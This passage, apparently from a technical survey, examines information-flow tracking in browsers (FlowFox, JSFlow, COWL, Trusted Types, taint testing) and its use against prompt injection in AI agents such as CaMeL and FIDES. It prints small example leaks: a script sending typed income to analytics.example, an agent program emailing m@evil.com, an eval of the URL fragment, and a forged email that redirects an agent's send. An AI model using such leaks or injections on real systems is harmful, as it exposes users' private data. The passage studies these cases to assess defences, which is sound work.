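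The tests also leave out the overhead of fixing false stops. A site might need upgrade annotations or a more detailed policy before its scripts could finish. WebPol's policies would also add overhead beyond that of the tracking.

### Network time

Rajani and colleagues timed only the scripts that ran while each website loaded. They say the overhead would be negligible if the baseline included network delays and the time to draw the page, but they report no measurement of this.

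Suppose the loan page takes two seconds to load and its scripts account for 300 milliseconds of that. A 32% overhead on the scripts adds 96 milliseconds, which is about 5% of the loading time. On a slower connection, the page might take six seconds, and the same delay from the same monitor would be less than 2%.

A visitor may not notice an extra 96 milliseconds while a page loads. But when the visitor types an income, the script that responds to each key press may not need the network, so no network delay would hide the extra time. Neither WebKit test included user interaction, although data that visitors type is one of the main things these systems are meant to protect.

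To measure FlowFox's 20% slowdown, De Groef and colleagues recorded six interactive tasks, such as sending a message on Facebook and adding a book to an Amazon basket, and replayed them in both browsers. The measured times include waiting for the websites' servers. If FlowFox doubled the time spent on scripts, a 20% total increase would mean that scripts took about a fifth of the original time. A task with more computation would slow down more.

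### A fairer measurement

All these figures come from browser engines that are now more than ten years old. A new test could avoid most of the problems above:

1. **Use a current browser with every compiler on as the baseline.** If tracking requires switching one off, time the ordinary browser both ways to separate that cost from the cost of the labels.
2. **Time the modified browser with tracking off, then on.** De Groef and colleagues did this and found that FlowFox's changes to the engine slowed some programs even when it ran them only once.
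3. **Test computation, DOM functions, page loading and typing separately.** Report the first run as well as later ones, because compilation affects them differently.
4. **Replay saved copies of websites.** Live pages change too much. When Kerschbaumer and colleagues visited newsarama.com on two consecutive days, the number of content requests rose from 11 to 18.
5. **Use a realistic policy and vary the number of labels.** Chudnov and Naumann timed JEST with a trivial policy. A page with data from 12 domains may behave very differently, especially under multi-execution.
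6. **Run the tests with enforcement on and off.** Count the scripts that stop, and compare running times only for those that finish.
7. **Include programs that try to leak data.** The three-line leak from the introduction and a leak through an exception would show whether a fast system is skipping necessary work.
8. **Report milliseconds and memory as well as percentages.** For page loading, give the time spent on scripts and the total time side by side.

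## Testing whether real websites still work

The timing tests of the WebKit monitor let scripts continue after a violation, so they couldn't show how many websites would work with enforcement switched on. A page can fail under enforcement for three reasons, and each needs a different repair:

- **Unsupported feature:** the script uses something the system doesn't implement, such as strict mode in JSFlow or the `with` statement in JEST. More programming solves this.
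- **False stop:** the script obeys the policy, but the monitor halts it anyway. The script needs annotations, or the monitor needs to be more precise.
- **Correct stop:** the script breaks the policy, and the page relies on what the script was doing. Loan calculators that share their input with third parties fail in this way under JSFlow's baseline policy. Someone has to change the site or loosen the policy.

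A single count of broken pages would mix gaps in the programming, limits of the method and choices in the policy.

### FlowFox on 500 home pages

De Groef and colleagues tested FlowFox on the 500 most popular websites, as ranked by the web-traffic company Alexa. Their policy made reading the cookie high, and they expected most sites to comply with it. The test had four steps:

1. A crawler opened each site in two ordinary copies of Firefox and in FlowFox, and took a screenshot in each browser once the page had loaded.
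2. The researchers compared the two Firefox screenshots and set aside every pixel that differed. This *mask* covered the parts of a page that change on every visit, such as advertisements, slideshows and timestamps.
3. They compared FlowFox's screenshot with one of the Firefox screenshots outside the mask. It didn't matter which one, because the two were identical there.
4. They recorded what share of the unmasked area differed.

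Most masks were small. The large ones came mainly from screen-filling images that changed between visits, or from a horizontal bar that appeared in only one of the two Firefox copies and pushed the rest of the page down.

Outside the masks, the differences between FlowFox and Firefox were usually small or zero. De Groef and colleagues plot the distribution, but they set no threshold above which a page counts as broken and give no number of broken pages. They inspected the larger differences by hand and found four main causes:

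- content that didn't appear
- content in a different position
- network delays, so that something had loaded in one browser but not yet in the other
- changing images that the mask had missed

Delays and changing images are measurement artifacts, but missing or displaced content could be a real failure, and the researchers don't report how many pages had it. They conclude that FlowFox doesn't break sites that comply with the policy. This is plausible for most of the 500 home pages, but the screenshots alone don't establish it.

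The size of the differing area is also a poor measure of harm. In a screenshot 1,280 pixels wide and 800 high, one wrong digit in a monthly instalment might change 150 of about a million pixels, or about 0.015%, and still mislead the visitor. A bar that moves the whole page down changes far more pixels but harms nobody. The mask also hides advertisements and slideshows, which are often the most script-heavy parts of a page.

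The policy made the test easier to pass. On a first visit, a script that reads the cookie often finds little or nothing, so the empty string FlowFox returns by default may be close to the real value. On later visits, the browser attaches the cookie to each request, so a visitor can stay logged in even if no script can read it. A policy that protects what visitors type would interfere with much more of what scripts do, but the crawler entered no text, so the test did not cover this.

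### Logged-in visits

A crawl of home pages involves little interaction, so De Groef and colleagues also checked how FlowFox behaved in the six recorded tasks from their timing tests. The tasks used Google, Facebook, Yahoo's webmail, Wikipedia, Blogspot and Amazon, each from a different category of site. In the Yahoo task, a logged-in user wrote an email, sent it and waited for the confirmation. In the Blogspot task, the user wrote a post, saved it and closed the editor.

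The researchers couldn't distinguish FlowFox's behaviour from Firefox's in any of these tasks. This is better evidence than a screenshot, because sending an email requires the page's scripts and the server to work together correctly.

They also tested a policy against tracking on sites that track behaviour, including those of Microsoft and the British newspaper The Sun. The user selected pieces of text and, on Microsoft's site, clicked on menu items. FlowFox replaced the tracked data with default values, and the pages still worked for the user.

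These results probably reflect some tuning, because De Groef had to change a few defaults that crashed the low-security run. A browser vendor couldn't do this by hand for every site.

### A check that is always true

JSFlow's developers tested far fewer pages but protected what visitors typed, and they had more trouble. Hedin and colleagues estimate, without giving a count, that most pages would need annotations if JSFlow relied on runtime tracking alone. For their experiments they added a simple *hybrid* analysis, in which the monitor also inspects code that hasn't run yet. It raised the labels of local variables before the script entered a secret branch, which removed many of the false stops. Most of the annotations they still needed were for other locations, such as object properties.

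The two null checks that Hedin and colleagues had to declassify by hand were only safeguards against bugs and differences between browsers. This small script contains a similar check:

```
settings = { ready: false };
if (income !== null) { settings.ready = true; }
send(settings.ready);
```

Here `income` is the secret text from the form, and `send` passes a value to the analytics company. The text may be empty, but it is never null, so the company always receives true and learns nothing. JSFlow still stops the script on the second line, because `settings.ready` is low and the pc is high.

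An upgrade annotation allows the write. The first line becomes:

```
settings = { ready: upg false to income };
```

The script now gets past the second line, but `settings.ready` is secret, so JSFlow stops the script at `send` instead. The annotation is enough only if the script uses the value within the page, for instance to decide whether to show a button.

A testing tool can find the place for such an annotation automatically. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues, 2019) used one on 56 programs. Most needed no upgrade annotations, and one needed 28. The tool can only find problems on paths that the tests reach. In the example, the branch always runs, so the first test would reveal the stop. With the annotation added, the script would still fail at `send`.

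The third remedy, from *Value-sensitive Hybrid Information Flow Control for a JavaScript-like Language* (Hedin, Bello and Sabelfeld, 2015), is for the monitor to look ahead. When a script reaches a secret branch, the monitor pauses while a static analysis finds everything the branch might write to and raises those labels, whether or not the branch will run. In the example, the analysis finds the write to `settings.ready` and makes that property secret in advance. The script needs no annotations, but `send` still fails.

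The last remedy, *value sensitivity*, is the only one that deals with the cause. Bello, Hedin and Sabelfeld propose it in *Value Sensitivity and Observable Abstract Values for Information Flow Control*. The monitor takes more account of the values themselves when it assigns labels. For the null checks, this can mean treating a value's type separately from its content. What the visitor typed is secret, but the fact that it is text, and therefore not null, is public. The condition on the second line is then public, so `settings.ready` stays low and the script can send it.

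Hedin and colleagues expect value sensitivity to handle both of the null checks they found easily, but JSFlow didn't have it at the time.

### Looking ahead through a function call

The look-ahead is more useful when the data is hard to reach from outside. Hedin, Bello and Sabelfeld give an example abstracted from the code of Google Analytics, shortened here:

```
function makeMemory() {
  var data = null;
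  return { set: function (d) { data = d; } };
}
m = makeMemory();
if (h) { m.set(true); }
```

The last line changes `data` under a high pc, so JSFlow stops the script when h is true, even if nothing ever reads `data`. The page's own code can't raise the label of `data` directly, because only functions inside `makeMemory` can refer to that variable. The annotation to raise the label would have to go into the analytics script, whose author may not know which of the page's values are secret.

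The look-ahead can use public values that exist while the script runs. Since m is public, the analysis can determine which function `m.set` refers to at that moment, follow the call and raise the label of `data`. It does this whether h is true or false, so the label does not reveal h.

If the static analysis can't determine where a branch will write, it can leave the labels unchanged. The no-sensitive-upgrade rule still applies when the branch runs, so a missed write can stop the program unnecessarily but can't cause a leak. Because the security guarantee comes entirely from the runtime monitor, the developers can improve the static analysis without risking security.

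Hedin and colleagues proved that their hybrid monitor accepts every program that a conventional static analysis of the same language accepts. The language is small: it includes `eval`, `with` and functions as values but leaves out exceptions, prototypes and automatic conversions. The implementation is a separate interpreter written in Haskell. The later paper on JSFlow reports that the approach can handle all the false stops that remained in the website experiments, but work on building it into JSFlow was still under way. Hedin and colleagues also point out that no such analysis can remove every false stop, because no algorithm can decide for every program whether it leaks.

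### Alerts on a million pages

Vogt, Nentwich and colleagues (2007) had earlier measured how often a browser that tracks sensitive data would interrupt its user. In *Cross-Site Scripting Prevention with Dynamic Data Tainting and Static Analysis*, they modified Firefox to protect visitors from scripts that attackers had injected into a site. When a script tried to send sensitive data to another domain, the browser asked the user whether to allow it.

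Their browser already used a form of look-ahead. At a branch that depended on sensitive data, it labeled everything the branch might change. If the branch contained a function call or `eval`, the browser treated every instruction that ran afterwards as dependent on sensitive data. This avoids stopping the script but can label far more data than necessary. The 2015 system instead leaves uncertain writes to the monitor, which occasionally stops a script by mistake.

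Vogt and colleagues had a crawler visit 1,033,000 pages, at most 100 per domain. The crawler filled in forms and triggered events such as clicks, so it exercised more code than FlowFox's crawler did.

| What raised an alert | Pages or alerts | Share of pages |
|---|---|---|
| Any sensitive data sent to another domain | 88,589 | 8.58% |
| The same, with fixed rules for 30 destinations | 13,964 | 1.35% |
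| Cookies only, with the same 30 rules | 5,289 | 0.51% |

Hedin and colleagues later described the 1.35% as a share of websites, but Vogt and colleagues counted individual pages. If their browsing resembled the crawl, someone who viewed 100 pages a day would see eight or nine alerts a day at the highest rate and one every two days at the lowest. The browser could also save a decision, which would further reduce the number of alerts.

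Most of the alerts were about real transfers, so the alert rates aren't false-alarm rates. The data went mainly to companies that measured traffic or tracked visitors, with google-analytics.com alone receiving 35,238 flows. The sites' owners had included those companies' scripts deliberately, so the alerts didn't reveal the attacks that the researchers wanted to stop. In a small sample of the cookie alerts, some transfers stayed within one company, such as those between cnn.net and cnn.com. The browser had tracked this data correctly, but its policy treated two domains with the same owner as unrelated.

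The figures also don't show how many pages would break. Vogt and colleagues suggest automatically blocking all suspicious transfers for inexperienced users and expect this to affect legitimate functions only rarely, but they didn't report testing the pages with those transfers blocked. Blocking a tracking request usually makes no difference to the visitor, but the site's owner loses the statistics, so a correct block may still stop something the owner relies on.

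### How often implicit flows matter

Most false stops come from trying to catch implicit flows. Staicu and colleagues investigated whether real programs contain enough of these flows to justify the effort. They studied 46 Node.js programs and ten browser scripts, all with known security problems. Most of the Node.js problems let an attacker run code on the server or slow it down with a carefully chosen input. The browser scripts sniffed the visitor's history or identified the browser by features such as its installed fonts.

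Staicu and colleagues call an implicit flow *observable* if it comes from a branch that runs and *hidden* if it comes from one that doesn't. If `l` starts as `false`, the flow from `h` to `l` in `if (h) { l = true; }` is observable when `h` is true and hidden when `h` is false.

Taint tracking, which ignores both observable and hidden flows, was enough to detect the problem in every Node.js program. For some of the browser scripts, detection also required tracking observable flows. A script that looks for installed fonts, for example, can measure the width of a piece of text and record a font as present if the width has a certain value. It sends the record, not the width, so the information passes through a branch. Hidden flows occurred in only five of the 56 programs, and detecting the known problems never required tracking them.

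In five Node.js programs, tracking implicit flows also led to additional reports of data reaching a forbidden sink, all of them false. One reason is that an implicit flow often matters less for integrity than for secrecy. If an attacker's input decides whether a program stores a constant, the attacker still can't change what the constant contains, so passing it to `eval` wouldn't let them inject code. If the input were a secret, however, the presence of the constant could reveal it.

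The researchers also counted the places in the code where a monitor would stop a program. They compared the no-sensitive-upgrade rule with Austin and Flanagan's *permissive-upgrade* rule, which marks values as partially leaked, much like the WebKit monitor's deferred check. The no-sensitive-upgrade rule raised 5.46 times as many alarms on average. Even under the permissive rule, most alarms didn't correspond to any flow from a source to a forbidden sink.

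Tracking costs work and precision too. The table gives the average number of operations on sensitive data that the tool had to track in the browser scripts, which serves as a rough measure of the slowdown:

| Flows tracked | Operations |
|---|---|
| Explicit | 5,919 |
| Explicit and observable implicit | 19,555 |
| All three kinds | 20,890 |

Across all the programs, taint tracking also labeled a 45.4% smaller share of the data as sensitive than tracking that included observable flows. Adding hidden flows barely changed the share. Observable flows therefore account for most of the extra work and labels, while the protection against hidden flows causes programs to stop.

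It would be risky to conclude that browsers can ignore hidden flows, because the researchers chose programs with known problems, most of them written by honest programmers who had made mistakes. An attacker who expects the browser to track data can use a hidden flow on purpose, as in the three-line leak from the introduction. Staicu and colleagues acknowledge that stronger defences could push attackers to do this. Their tool also finds hidden flows only where the tests lead it to insert upgrades, and the tests covered both outcomes of every sensitive branch in just 54% of the programs.

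The study gives site owners a good reason to use taint tracking to find mistakes in trusted code, but a browser that has to contain a hostile script still needs protection against hidden flows.

### A visible stop or a silent change

Secure multi-execution has no false stops of this kind, but it can change a page without warning. Which behaviour is better depends on what the visitor does with the result.

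Suppose the loan calculator sends the income to the lender's server to get a quote, but the policy mislabels this request as low. A monitor blocks the request, so the visitor gets no quote. FlowFox instead sends the request with the default income, say 0. The page then displays a quote for someone who earns nothing, and the visitor may believe it. The difference would hardly show in the screenshot test, because only a few digits would change.

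Silently giving a tracking script default values is better than halting it. The visitor loses nothing if the script collects those values, but halting it could disable other functions in the same file.

A visible stop also helps the developer, because the error identifies a line of code. The developer can check whether the script was leaking and then add an annotation or change the policy. FlowFox changes behavior silently, so the developer might learn of a problem only when a customer complains about a strange quote. Hedin and colleagues list as an open question whether such changes, including messages sent in a different order, cause trouble in practice. FlowFox's logged-in tests are encouraging, but their policies covered cookies and tracking data, where a wrong value rarely affects what the visitor sees.

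The researchers also differ on how much breakage is acceptable. De Groef writes that a security measure for the web needs an almost complete guarantee that it won't spoil the user's experience. Hedin and colleagues think a few false stops need not prevent adoption, because responsible site owners can annotate their own code. Each view is reasonable for a different user of the technology. A browser vendor can't repair other people's websites, so even a low failure rate would affect many visitors. The owner of a single loan calculator can test every function before turning enforcement on, and would be better served by a monitor that fails visibly.

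## What browsers and security testers adopted instead

No major browser tracks labels through the scripts it runs. Mozilla planned to build such tracking into Firefox, and other researchers tried coarser labels that did not require changing the JavaScript engine. Browsers eventually shipped restrictions on what a page may load and which text it may run as code, while security testers adopted taint tracking.

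### FlowSafe

In August 2009, Mozilla's *Security/Research* (2009) listed a project called FlowSafe. Its participants included Brendan Eich, who created JavaScript and was Mozilla's chief technology officer at the time; Cormac Flanagan, who had helped devise the no-sensitive-upgrade rule; and Michael Franz, whose group later added labels to WebKit.

In Mozilla's *FlowSafe* (2009), Eich set out a plan to replace a security model "stuck" at the same-origin policy since 1995, and to do so without breaking the web. Firefox would protect pages from advertising and analytics scripts by default and guarantee noninterference for runs that terminate. The planned work included labels for scripts, the program counter, objects and the DOM. Declassification was left for later, although many real pages need it.

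Eich's slides, *JavaScript Security*, also explain how the team hoped to avoid "losing the JS performance wars". Most data on a page comes from the page's own origin, so only values from elsewhere would need an explicit label. In an early prototype written in the language SML, labeling every value made programs take 1.7 times as long, and this *sparse labeling* reduced the factor to 1.2. The prototype was not a browser, so these figures are weak evidence of how much labeling would slow Firefox.

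The slides also list open problems. Eich asked whether a browser that halts scripts would be usable, and suggested that it might need some help from static analysis.

Mozilla never shipped FlowSafe in Firefox, and the FlowSafe project page gives no reason. The closest to an explanation from a participant is a general remark by Kerschbaumer and colleagues, including Franz, who wrote in 2013 that the runtime overhead of information-flow tracking prevented its adoption. Someone later offered to help with a Mozilla bug report that apparently concerned taint tracking. One developer replied that he hadn't touched the work in a long time, and another pointed to COWL, a newer proposal with coarser labels.

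In their slides for *Protecting Users by Confining JavaScript with COWL*, Stefan, Yang and colleagues (2014) treat the JavaScript engine as off limits. The team, which included researchers at Mozilla and Google, warns that adding even one instruction to a frequently run path would keep a change out of the official browser. This is their judgement rather than a vendor's stated rule, but it would exclude nearly every monitor that labels individual values.

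### One label for a group of frames

Labeling whole frames lets a browser track information flow without changes to its JavaScript engine. Yip, Narula and colleagues did this in *Privacy-Preserving Browser-Side Scripting With BFlow* (2009), using a Firefox extension of about 1,000 lines of JavaScript and a matching layer on the web server.

BFlow groups frames into *protection zones*, each with one label. The label is a set of tags for the kinds of confidential data that the zone may have seen. A script in zone S may send a message to zone R only if

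label of S ⊆ label of R

so the receiver must already carry every tag that the sender carries. Before a zone can read confidential data, it must add the data's tag to its label. From then on it can contact only the server that supplied the data, unless the site has declared an exception.

BFlow also sends the label with each request to a cooperating server running BFlow, which stores the label with the data and returns it later. This would have preserved the label on the visitor's figures at mlcalc.com, which was lost when they passed through the site's server.

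Scripts inside a BFlow zone can use all of JavaScript, including `eval`. Code they create runs under the zone's label, so BFlow needs no special rule for it. The label also covers implicit flows within the zone, because BFlow treats everything a script does there as confidential, whichever branch it takes.

To test compatibility, Yip and colleagues adapted 12 existing widgets, mostly for the blogging service Blogger. Seven needed no changes, and four needed changes to one or two lines. The last, a chat room that stored its messages on a server, needed changes to 89 lines. The researchers expected little slowdown but didn't measure it.

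This approach is less precise. If a blog's frame contains a confidential post, its scripts can't load even a fixed background picture from another server, because BFlow can't determine whether the post influenced the request. Yip and colleagues suggest that the blog's server fetch such pictures in advance. This doesn't help when the script needs the confidential data to choose what to fetch, as with a map of the user's address.

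### COWL and the loan calculator

COWL, short for Confinement with Origin Web Labels, gives a label to each page, frame or worker, where a worker is a script that runs separately from the page. It also lets a page label individual messages. Suppose the lender wants to use another company's script to compute instalments:

1. The page starts the script in a worker with a public label. The script downloads the latest interest rates from its own company's server.
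2. The page labels the income with the lender's origin and sends it to the worker.
3. To open the message, the worker must raise its label. COWL then cuts off its access to the other company's server.
4. The worker computes the instalment and returns it. The page has the authority to read the lender's data, so it can display the result.

COWL lets the script use the network freely until the script reads the income. A Content Security Policy can't express this change of permission, because the policy stays the same while the page is open.

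The design suits a calculation that a site can move into a worker, but it suits the analytics script less well. By default, a page can use data from its own origin without restriction, so a script included in the usual way would still have the page's full authority. The owner can give up that authority and confine the page, but then the analytics script can't report even harmless page views once the page contains the labeled income. JSFlow, by contrast, allowed Google's requests as long as nothing in them came from the visitor's input.

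Stefan and colleagues built COWL into Firefox and Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, adding about 4,000 lines of code to each without changing either JavaScript engine. They compared four small applications with versions split into the same parts but without security checks. The largest slowdown they reported was 16%, for an encrypted document editor that took 116 milliseconds instead of 100. They loaded everything from the same computer, so network delay didn't make the slowdown look smaller. On DOM tests that didn't use COWL, the slowdown was under 4%.

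These overheads are much smaller than those of the fine-grained monitors, but the guarantee is weaker. A confined script could still signal to an unconfined one, for instance by varying how long the browser takes to draw something. In its draft standard, W3C therefore presents COWL as protection against code that is "buggy but not malicious" and tells site owners not to give sensitive data to hostile code.

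COWL got further towards standardisation than FlowSafe. Hill (2014), in *Rechartering Thread 12*, reported strong support for it at W3C's annual meeting. In early 2015, Akhawe backed its aims but questioned whether the W3C group should commit to specifying COWL's whole label system. The group added COWL to its programme in March 2015 and published a first draft that October.

According to W3C's *Web Application Security Working Group Charter* (2024), the group dropped COWL in March 2019. The charter gives no reason. COWL reappears in W3C's *DRAFT Web Application Security Working Group Charter* (2026), but the latest version listed is still from October 2015. The draft also contains unfilled template text, so the entry is weak evidence of a revival.

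### Labels across the browser

BFlow and COWL dealt with web pages, but browser extensions can read pages too. In *Run-time Monitoring and Formal Analysis of Information Flows in Chromium* (2015), Bauer, Cai and colleagues labeled a much wider range of things, including pages, scripts, DOM elements, events, cookies, browsing history and extensions. In one of their examples, a password manager fills in a login form on a page where a malicious translation extension is also active. In an ordinary browser, the translation extension could read the password and send it to its own server, but the labels block that transfer.

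Their monitor treats the JavaScript engine as a closed box. It gives a script one label and checks that label when the script calls a browser function, not when it copies a variable. This saves a great deal of work inside the engine, but labels on individual page elements can bring back the three-line leak from the introduction. Here h, t and l stand for the contents of three elements. The element h is secret, and t and l both start as a public false:

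```
function first()  { if (!h) { t = true; } }
function second() { if (!t) { l = true; } }
```

Suppose the browser runs `first` and then `second` as handlers for separate events. If h is true, `first` changes nothing, so t is still public and `second` sets l to true. If h is false, `first` sets t to true and the monitor marks t as secret, so l stays false. In both cases, l ends up public and equal to h.

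Bauer and colleagues nevertheless proved noninterference for a model of their system. The model assumes an attacker doesn't know when or in what order the browser runs the handlers, and so can't infer anything about h from the value of l. They conceded that real browsers run handlers in a fairly predictable order, but expected most attacks to be less sophisticated than one that exploits this order.

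Monitors that used coarse labels could also be slow. Bauer and colleagues' monitor made the home pages of ten popular sites load 55% more slowly on average, and Wikipedia's took about twice as long to load. They hadn't optimised the prototype and believed an optimised version could be very efficient. Loading Wikipedia's page required 190 label checks and Amazon's 386, many of them while the browser built the DOM.

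The monitor took each page's label from its Content Security Policy, so compatibility depended on that policy. A page without one could load content only from its own site, and most such pages failed to load fully. The researchers had to write policies by hand for the 100 most popular sites.

### Which text may become code

Browsers ship two mechanisms against some of the same threats. One of them, Content Security Policy, began as a list of permitted servers, but it also controls code created at runtime. If a policy restricts scripts, the browser blocks `eval`, the `Function` constructor and timers that receive code as text. A site that needs them can add the keyword `'unsafe-eval'`, which permits them for every script on the page.

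*Trusted Types*, as the W3C describes it, makes powerful browser functions accept only typed values that a script can't forge, instead of plain strings. A site turns it on with a line in its Content Security Policy. `eval("x = 4")` then fails because its argument is a string. To run text as code, a script must first pass it through a function that the site has approved for this purpose.

For example, the loan page might download its monthly interest rate as a short sum, such as `0.05 / 12`. It could accept nothing except numbers and arithmetic:

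```
var rates = trustedTypes.createPolicy("rates", {
  createScript: function (text) {
    if (/^[0-9.+*\/() -]+$/.test(text)) { return text; }
    throw new TypeError("Not a sum");
  }
});
rate = eval(rates.createScript(downloadedText));
```

The page's Content Security Policy must still permit `eval`. When it does, `eval` accepts the special object that `createScript` returns. If an attacker replaces the sum with a program that reads the income field, the test fails and the program never runs.

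The special object that Trusted Types requires is a little like an integrity label, but it records only that the text passed through an approved function. An attacker who sends `0.02 / 12` passes the test, and the visitor sees a false instalment. If the site writes a function that approves every string, Trusted Types offers no protection.

All the major browsers support both mechanisms. Chrome has had Trusted Types since 2020, Safari added it in 2025 and Firefox followed in early 2026. W3C is still revising the specifications, with new drafts of both from the first half of 2026. Each site still has to write a policy and turn it on to be protected. Older pages that use `eval` or build HTML from strings may need changes first.

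### A permitted script can still send the income

Both mechanisms are good at keeping an attacker's code out of a page. They do much less about code that the owner has let in. Suppose the loan page permits scripts and images from its analytics company, enforces Trusted Types and forbids `eval`. The analytics script can still do this:

```
var income = document.getElementById("income").value;
new Image().src = "https://analytics.example/view?i=" + income;
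```

As in the introduction, the Content Security Policy allows the request because the server is on the list. Trusted Types also allows it because an image address is an ordinary string and the script doesn't turn any text into code. JSFlow would stop the script at the second line, and FlowFox would send a default value.

A page that can contact only its own server can still leak data. Stefan and colleagues describe a *self-exfiltration* attack, in which a script writes a password to a public part of the trusted site, where the attacker can read it. On the loan site, a script could post the income as a public comment.

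### Taint tracking as a testing tool

A security tester usually wants to find places where an attacker's text could become code. Foxhound, a modified version of Firefox developed with the software company SAP, tracks strings from sources such as the page's address to sinks such as `eval`. Suppose a loan page contains this line:

```
eval("rate = " + location.hash.slice(1));
```

The last part of the expression is whatever follows the # sign in the address. The tester opens the page with `#0.05` at the end, and the browser reports that text from the address has reached `eval`. The tester can then replace the number with a harmless command, such as one that opens an alert box. If the box appears, the bug is real, because an attacker could put a harmful command in a link instead.

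Trackers for Node.js, such as NodeMedic, apply the same method to code on servers. They follow the input passed to a package and report when it reaches a function that runs code or system commands.

Some researchers who had worked on enforcement also took up testing. Hennigan and colleagues described how Franz's group at Irvine offered its labels as a way to diagnose security holes. Two members of the team behind the Chromium monitor later led a project to help programmers and users detect script-injection attacks. *Towards a Usable, Practical, and Provably Secure Browser Infrastructure*, by Jia, Bauer and Fredrikson, describes a taint-tracking version of Chromium on which students have based research projects.

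Testing avoids several problems that kept information-flow tracking out of ordinary browsers. A tester can wait for a slow page, and the tool can report a flow without stopping the script. A false report takes up some of the tester's time but doesn't break the page for visitors.

The tester can also accept a tool that ignores implicit flows. To inject a command, an attacker usually needs the page to copy the text of that command into `eval`, and copying is an explicit flow. This is consistent with the earlier study of 56 programs, in which tracking explicit flows was enough to detect every known problem in the Node.js code. The tool will still miss some bugs. For example, a page might decode text by testing each character and adding a matching constant to a new string, and the attacker's command would then reach `eval` without its label.

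The tester misses one bug this way, and another test may reveal it. But if a browser that enforces a policy ignores implicit flows, the author of a hostile script can deliberately run the income through the same kind of decoder and send out the whole number on every visit.

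## Applying these methods to plans an AI agent writes at runtime

An AI agent is a language model connected to *tools*, functions that read email, open files, send messages or make payments. The model turns a user's request into a new plan, which is either a program or a series of tool calls. Nobody can inspect that plan in advance, just as nobody can inspect the text that a page will later pass to `eval`.

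Agents also read emails and web pages that strangers wrote. In a *prompt injection*, an attacker hides instructions in such text, and the model follows them as if they came from the user, so the attacker ends up writing part of the program.

Some links to the browser work are direct. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) cite Hedin and Sabelfeld's point that `eval` puts code beyond static analysis, and they track agents at runtime for the same reason. Other links, such as comparing tools with library models or applying multi-execution to an agent, are inferences from how the systems work.

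An agent's first problem is integrity, not secrecy, so its labels mostly separate trusted data from untrusted data instead of public from secret.

### A planner that never reads the email

The "Dual LLM" pattern is a defence that uses two models. A privileged model reads the user's request and calls tools, and only a quarantined model, which has no tools, reads untrusted text. The quarantined model returns its answer under a name such as `$email-summary-1`, which the privileged model can pass on without reading the answer itself. Willison proposed the pattern in 2023 and describes a flaw in it in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025).

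The pattern stops an email from adding a tool call, but the email can still change the data in a call already in the plan. In an example from *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025), text hidden in a calendar can alter the message an agent sends to a colleague.

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), adds information-flow tracking to the two models. Suppose a borrower asks an agent to send a loan offer to the address in the broker's last email. CaMeL works as follows:

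1. The privileged model writes a program in a restricted version of Python. It sees the request and the descriptions of the tools, but not the email.
2. A custom interpreter runs the program.
3. The interpreter gives each value *capabilities*, tags that record where the value came from and who may read it. It also tracks which values the program derived from which others.
4. Before each tool call, a policy checks the tags on the arguments. If the policy doesn't allow the call, CaMeL can refuse it or ask the user.

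The program might look like this:

```
email   = get_last_email("broker")
address = ask_quarantined("Find the broker's address", email)
offer   = read_file("loan_offer.pdf")
send_email(address, offer)
```

Like JSFlow, this design uses a custom interpreter that carries labels through each operation. The program's text depends only on trusted input, so under JSFlow's rule for `eval` the program would start with a trusted program counter (pc) label.

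### Sending the loan offer

If an attacker forges an email from the broker that gives a new address, the program doesn't change, but `address` holds the attacker's address.

A label monitor marks `address` as untrusted because it came from the email. If the policy requires a trusted recipient, the monitor stops the last line. It would also stop that line if the email were genuine, because the label records where the address came from, not whether it is correct.

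A policy about readers is more precise. It allows the call only if the recipient is on a list of people who may read the offer, so the agent can send it to the broker's usual address but not to the attacker's. However, somebody must have added the broker's address to the list beforehand, and in that case the agent had little need for the email.

A raised pc makes no difference here, because the program has no branches. It matters in a variant where the address comes from the borrower's own contacts:

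```
if ask_quarantined("Does the broker want the offer?", email):
    send_email(contacts["broker"], offer)
```

Both arguments now pass the policy, but whether the offer is sent depends on the email. A monitor that raises the pc label to "untrusted" inside the branch would again block the call, whether the email is genuine or forged.

Multi-execution would run the program twice. Only the trusted run could send the offer, and it would get a default value instead of the email's contents. If the default were the borrower's own address, the offer would go to the borrower in both cases, and neither the attacker nor the broker would receive it. In the variant with a branch, the agent would always send the offer if the default answer were "yes" and never if it were "no".

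The defence in *MELON* (2025) also uses a second run, but to detect attacks. The second run gets the same tool results as the first but a neutral task that typically needs no tools. If the model calls a tool anyway, the instruction to do so probably came from the data. MELON would probably miss the forged email, because the email contains a wrong address but no instruction.

### Branches in a CaMeL program

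CaMeL does track some implicit flows. Garby and colleagues give this example, in which the balance is secret:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL refuses to send the email because the condition depends on the balance. But it labels a variable only in a branch that runs, so the three-line leak from the introduction still works. A version for this example is:

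```
rich = True; tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and secret. The assignment on the third line doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. The no-sensitive-upgrade rule would have stopped the program on the second line.

This gap is less serious than it would be in a browser, where the author of a hostile script can write the leak directly. A CaMeL program comes from a model that hasn't read the attacker's text. But because of the gap, CaMeL's tracking can't guarantee noninterference for every program the model might write.

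Garby and colleagues found another leak outside the interpreter. When a program fails, CaMeL tries again in an ordinary Python loop that tracks no labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. This is the usual termination channel, but the loop can repeat it until the whole secret is revealed. CaMeL censors error messages to reduce the problem, but without a formal guarantee.

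The language also causes problems. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) points out that the restricted Python still has dynamic typing, exceptions and reflection (code that examines or changes itself). JavaScript has the same features, and they account for many of JSFlow's rules. The paper proposes a simpler language with bounded loops and explicit conditions. Switching languages would be far easier for agents than for the web, because no existing websites depend on the agents' current one. But the model would have to write in a language it has rarely or never seen.

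### A planner that reads as it goes

CaMeL writes its whole program before it reads any data, but many agents choose each tool call after seeing the result of the last one. Tracing a language model's answer to specific parts of its input is hard, so Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give each answer the combined label of everything the model has read. After the model reads one untrusted email, every later decision is untrusted, as if the pc label had been raised at a branch and never lowered.

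Their system, FIDES, avoids this by hiding data from the planner. If a tool's result is less trusted than the conversation so far, the planner receives only a variable name, such as `#read_emails_0`. It can pass this name to another tool or have a quarantined model process the contents.

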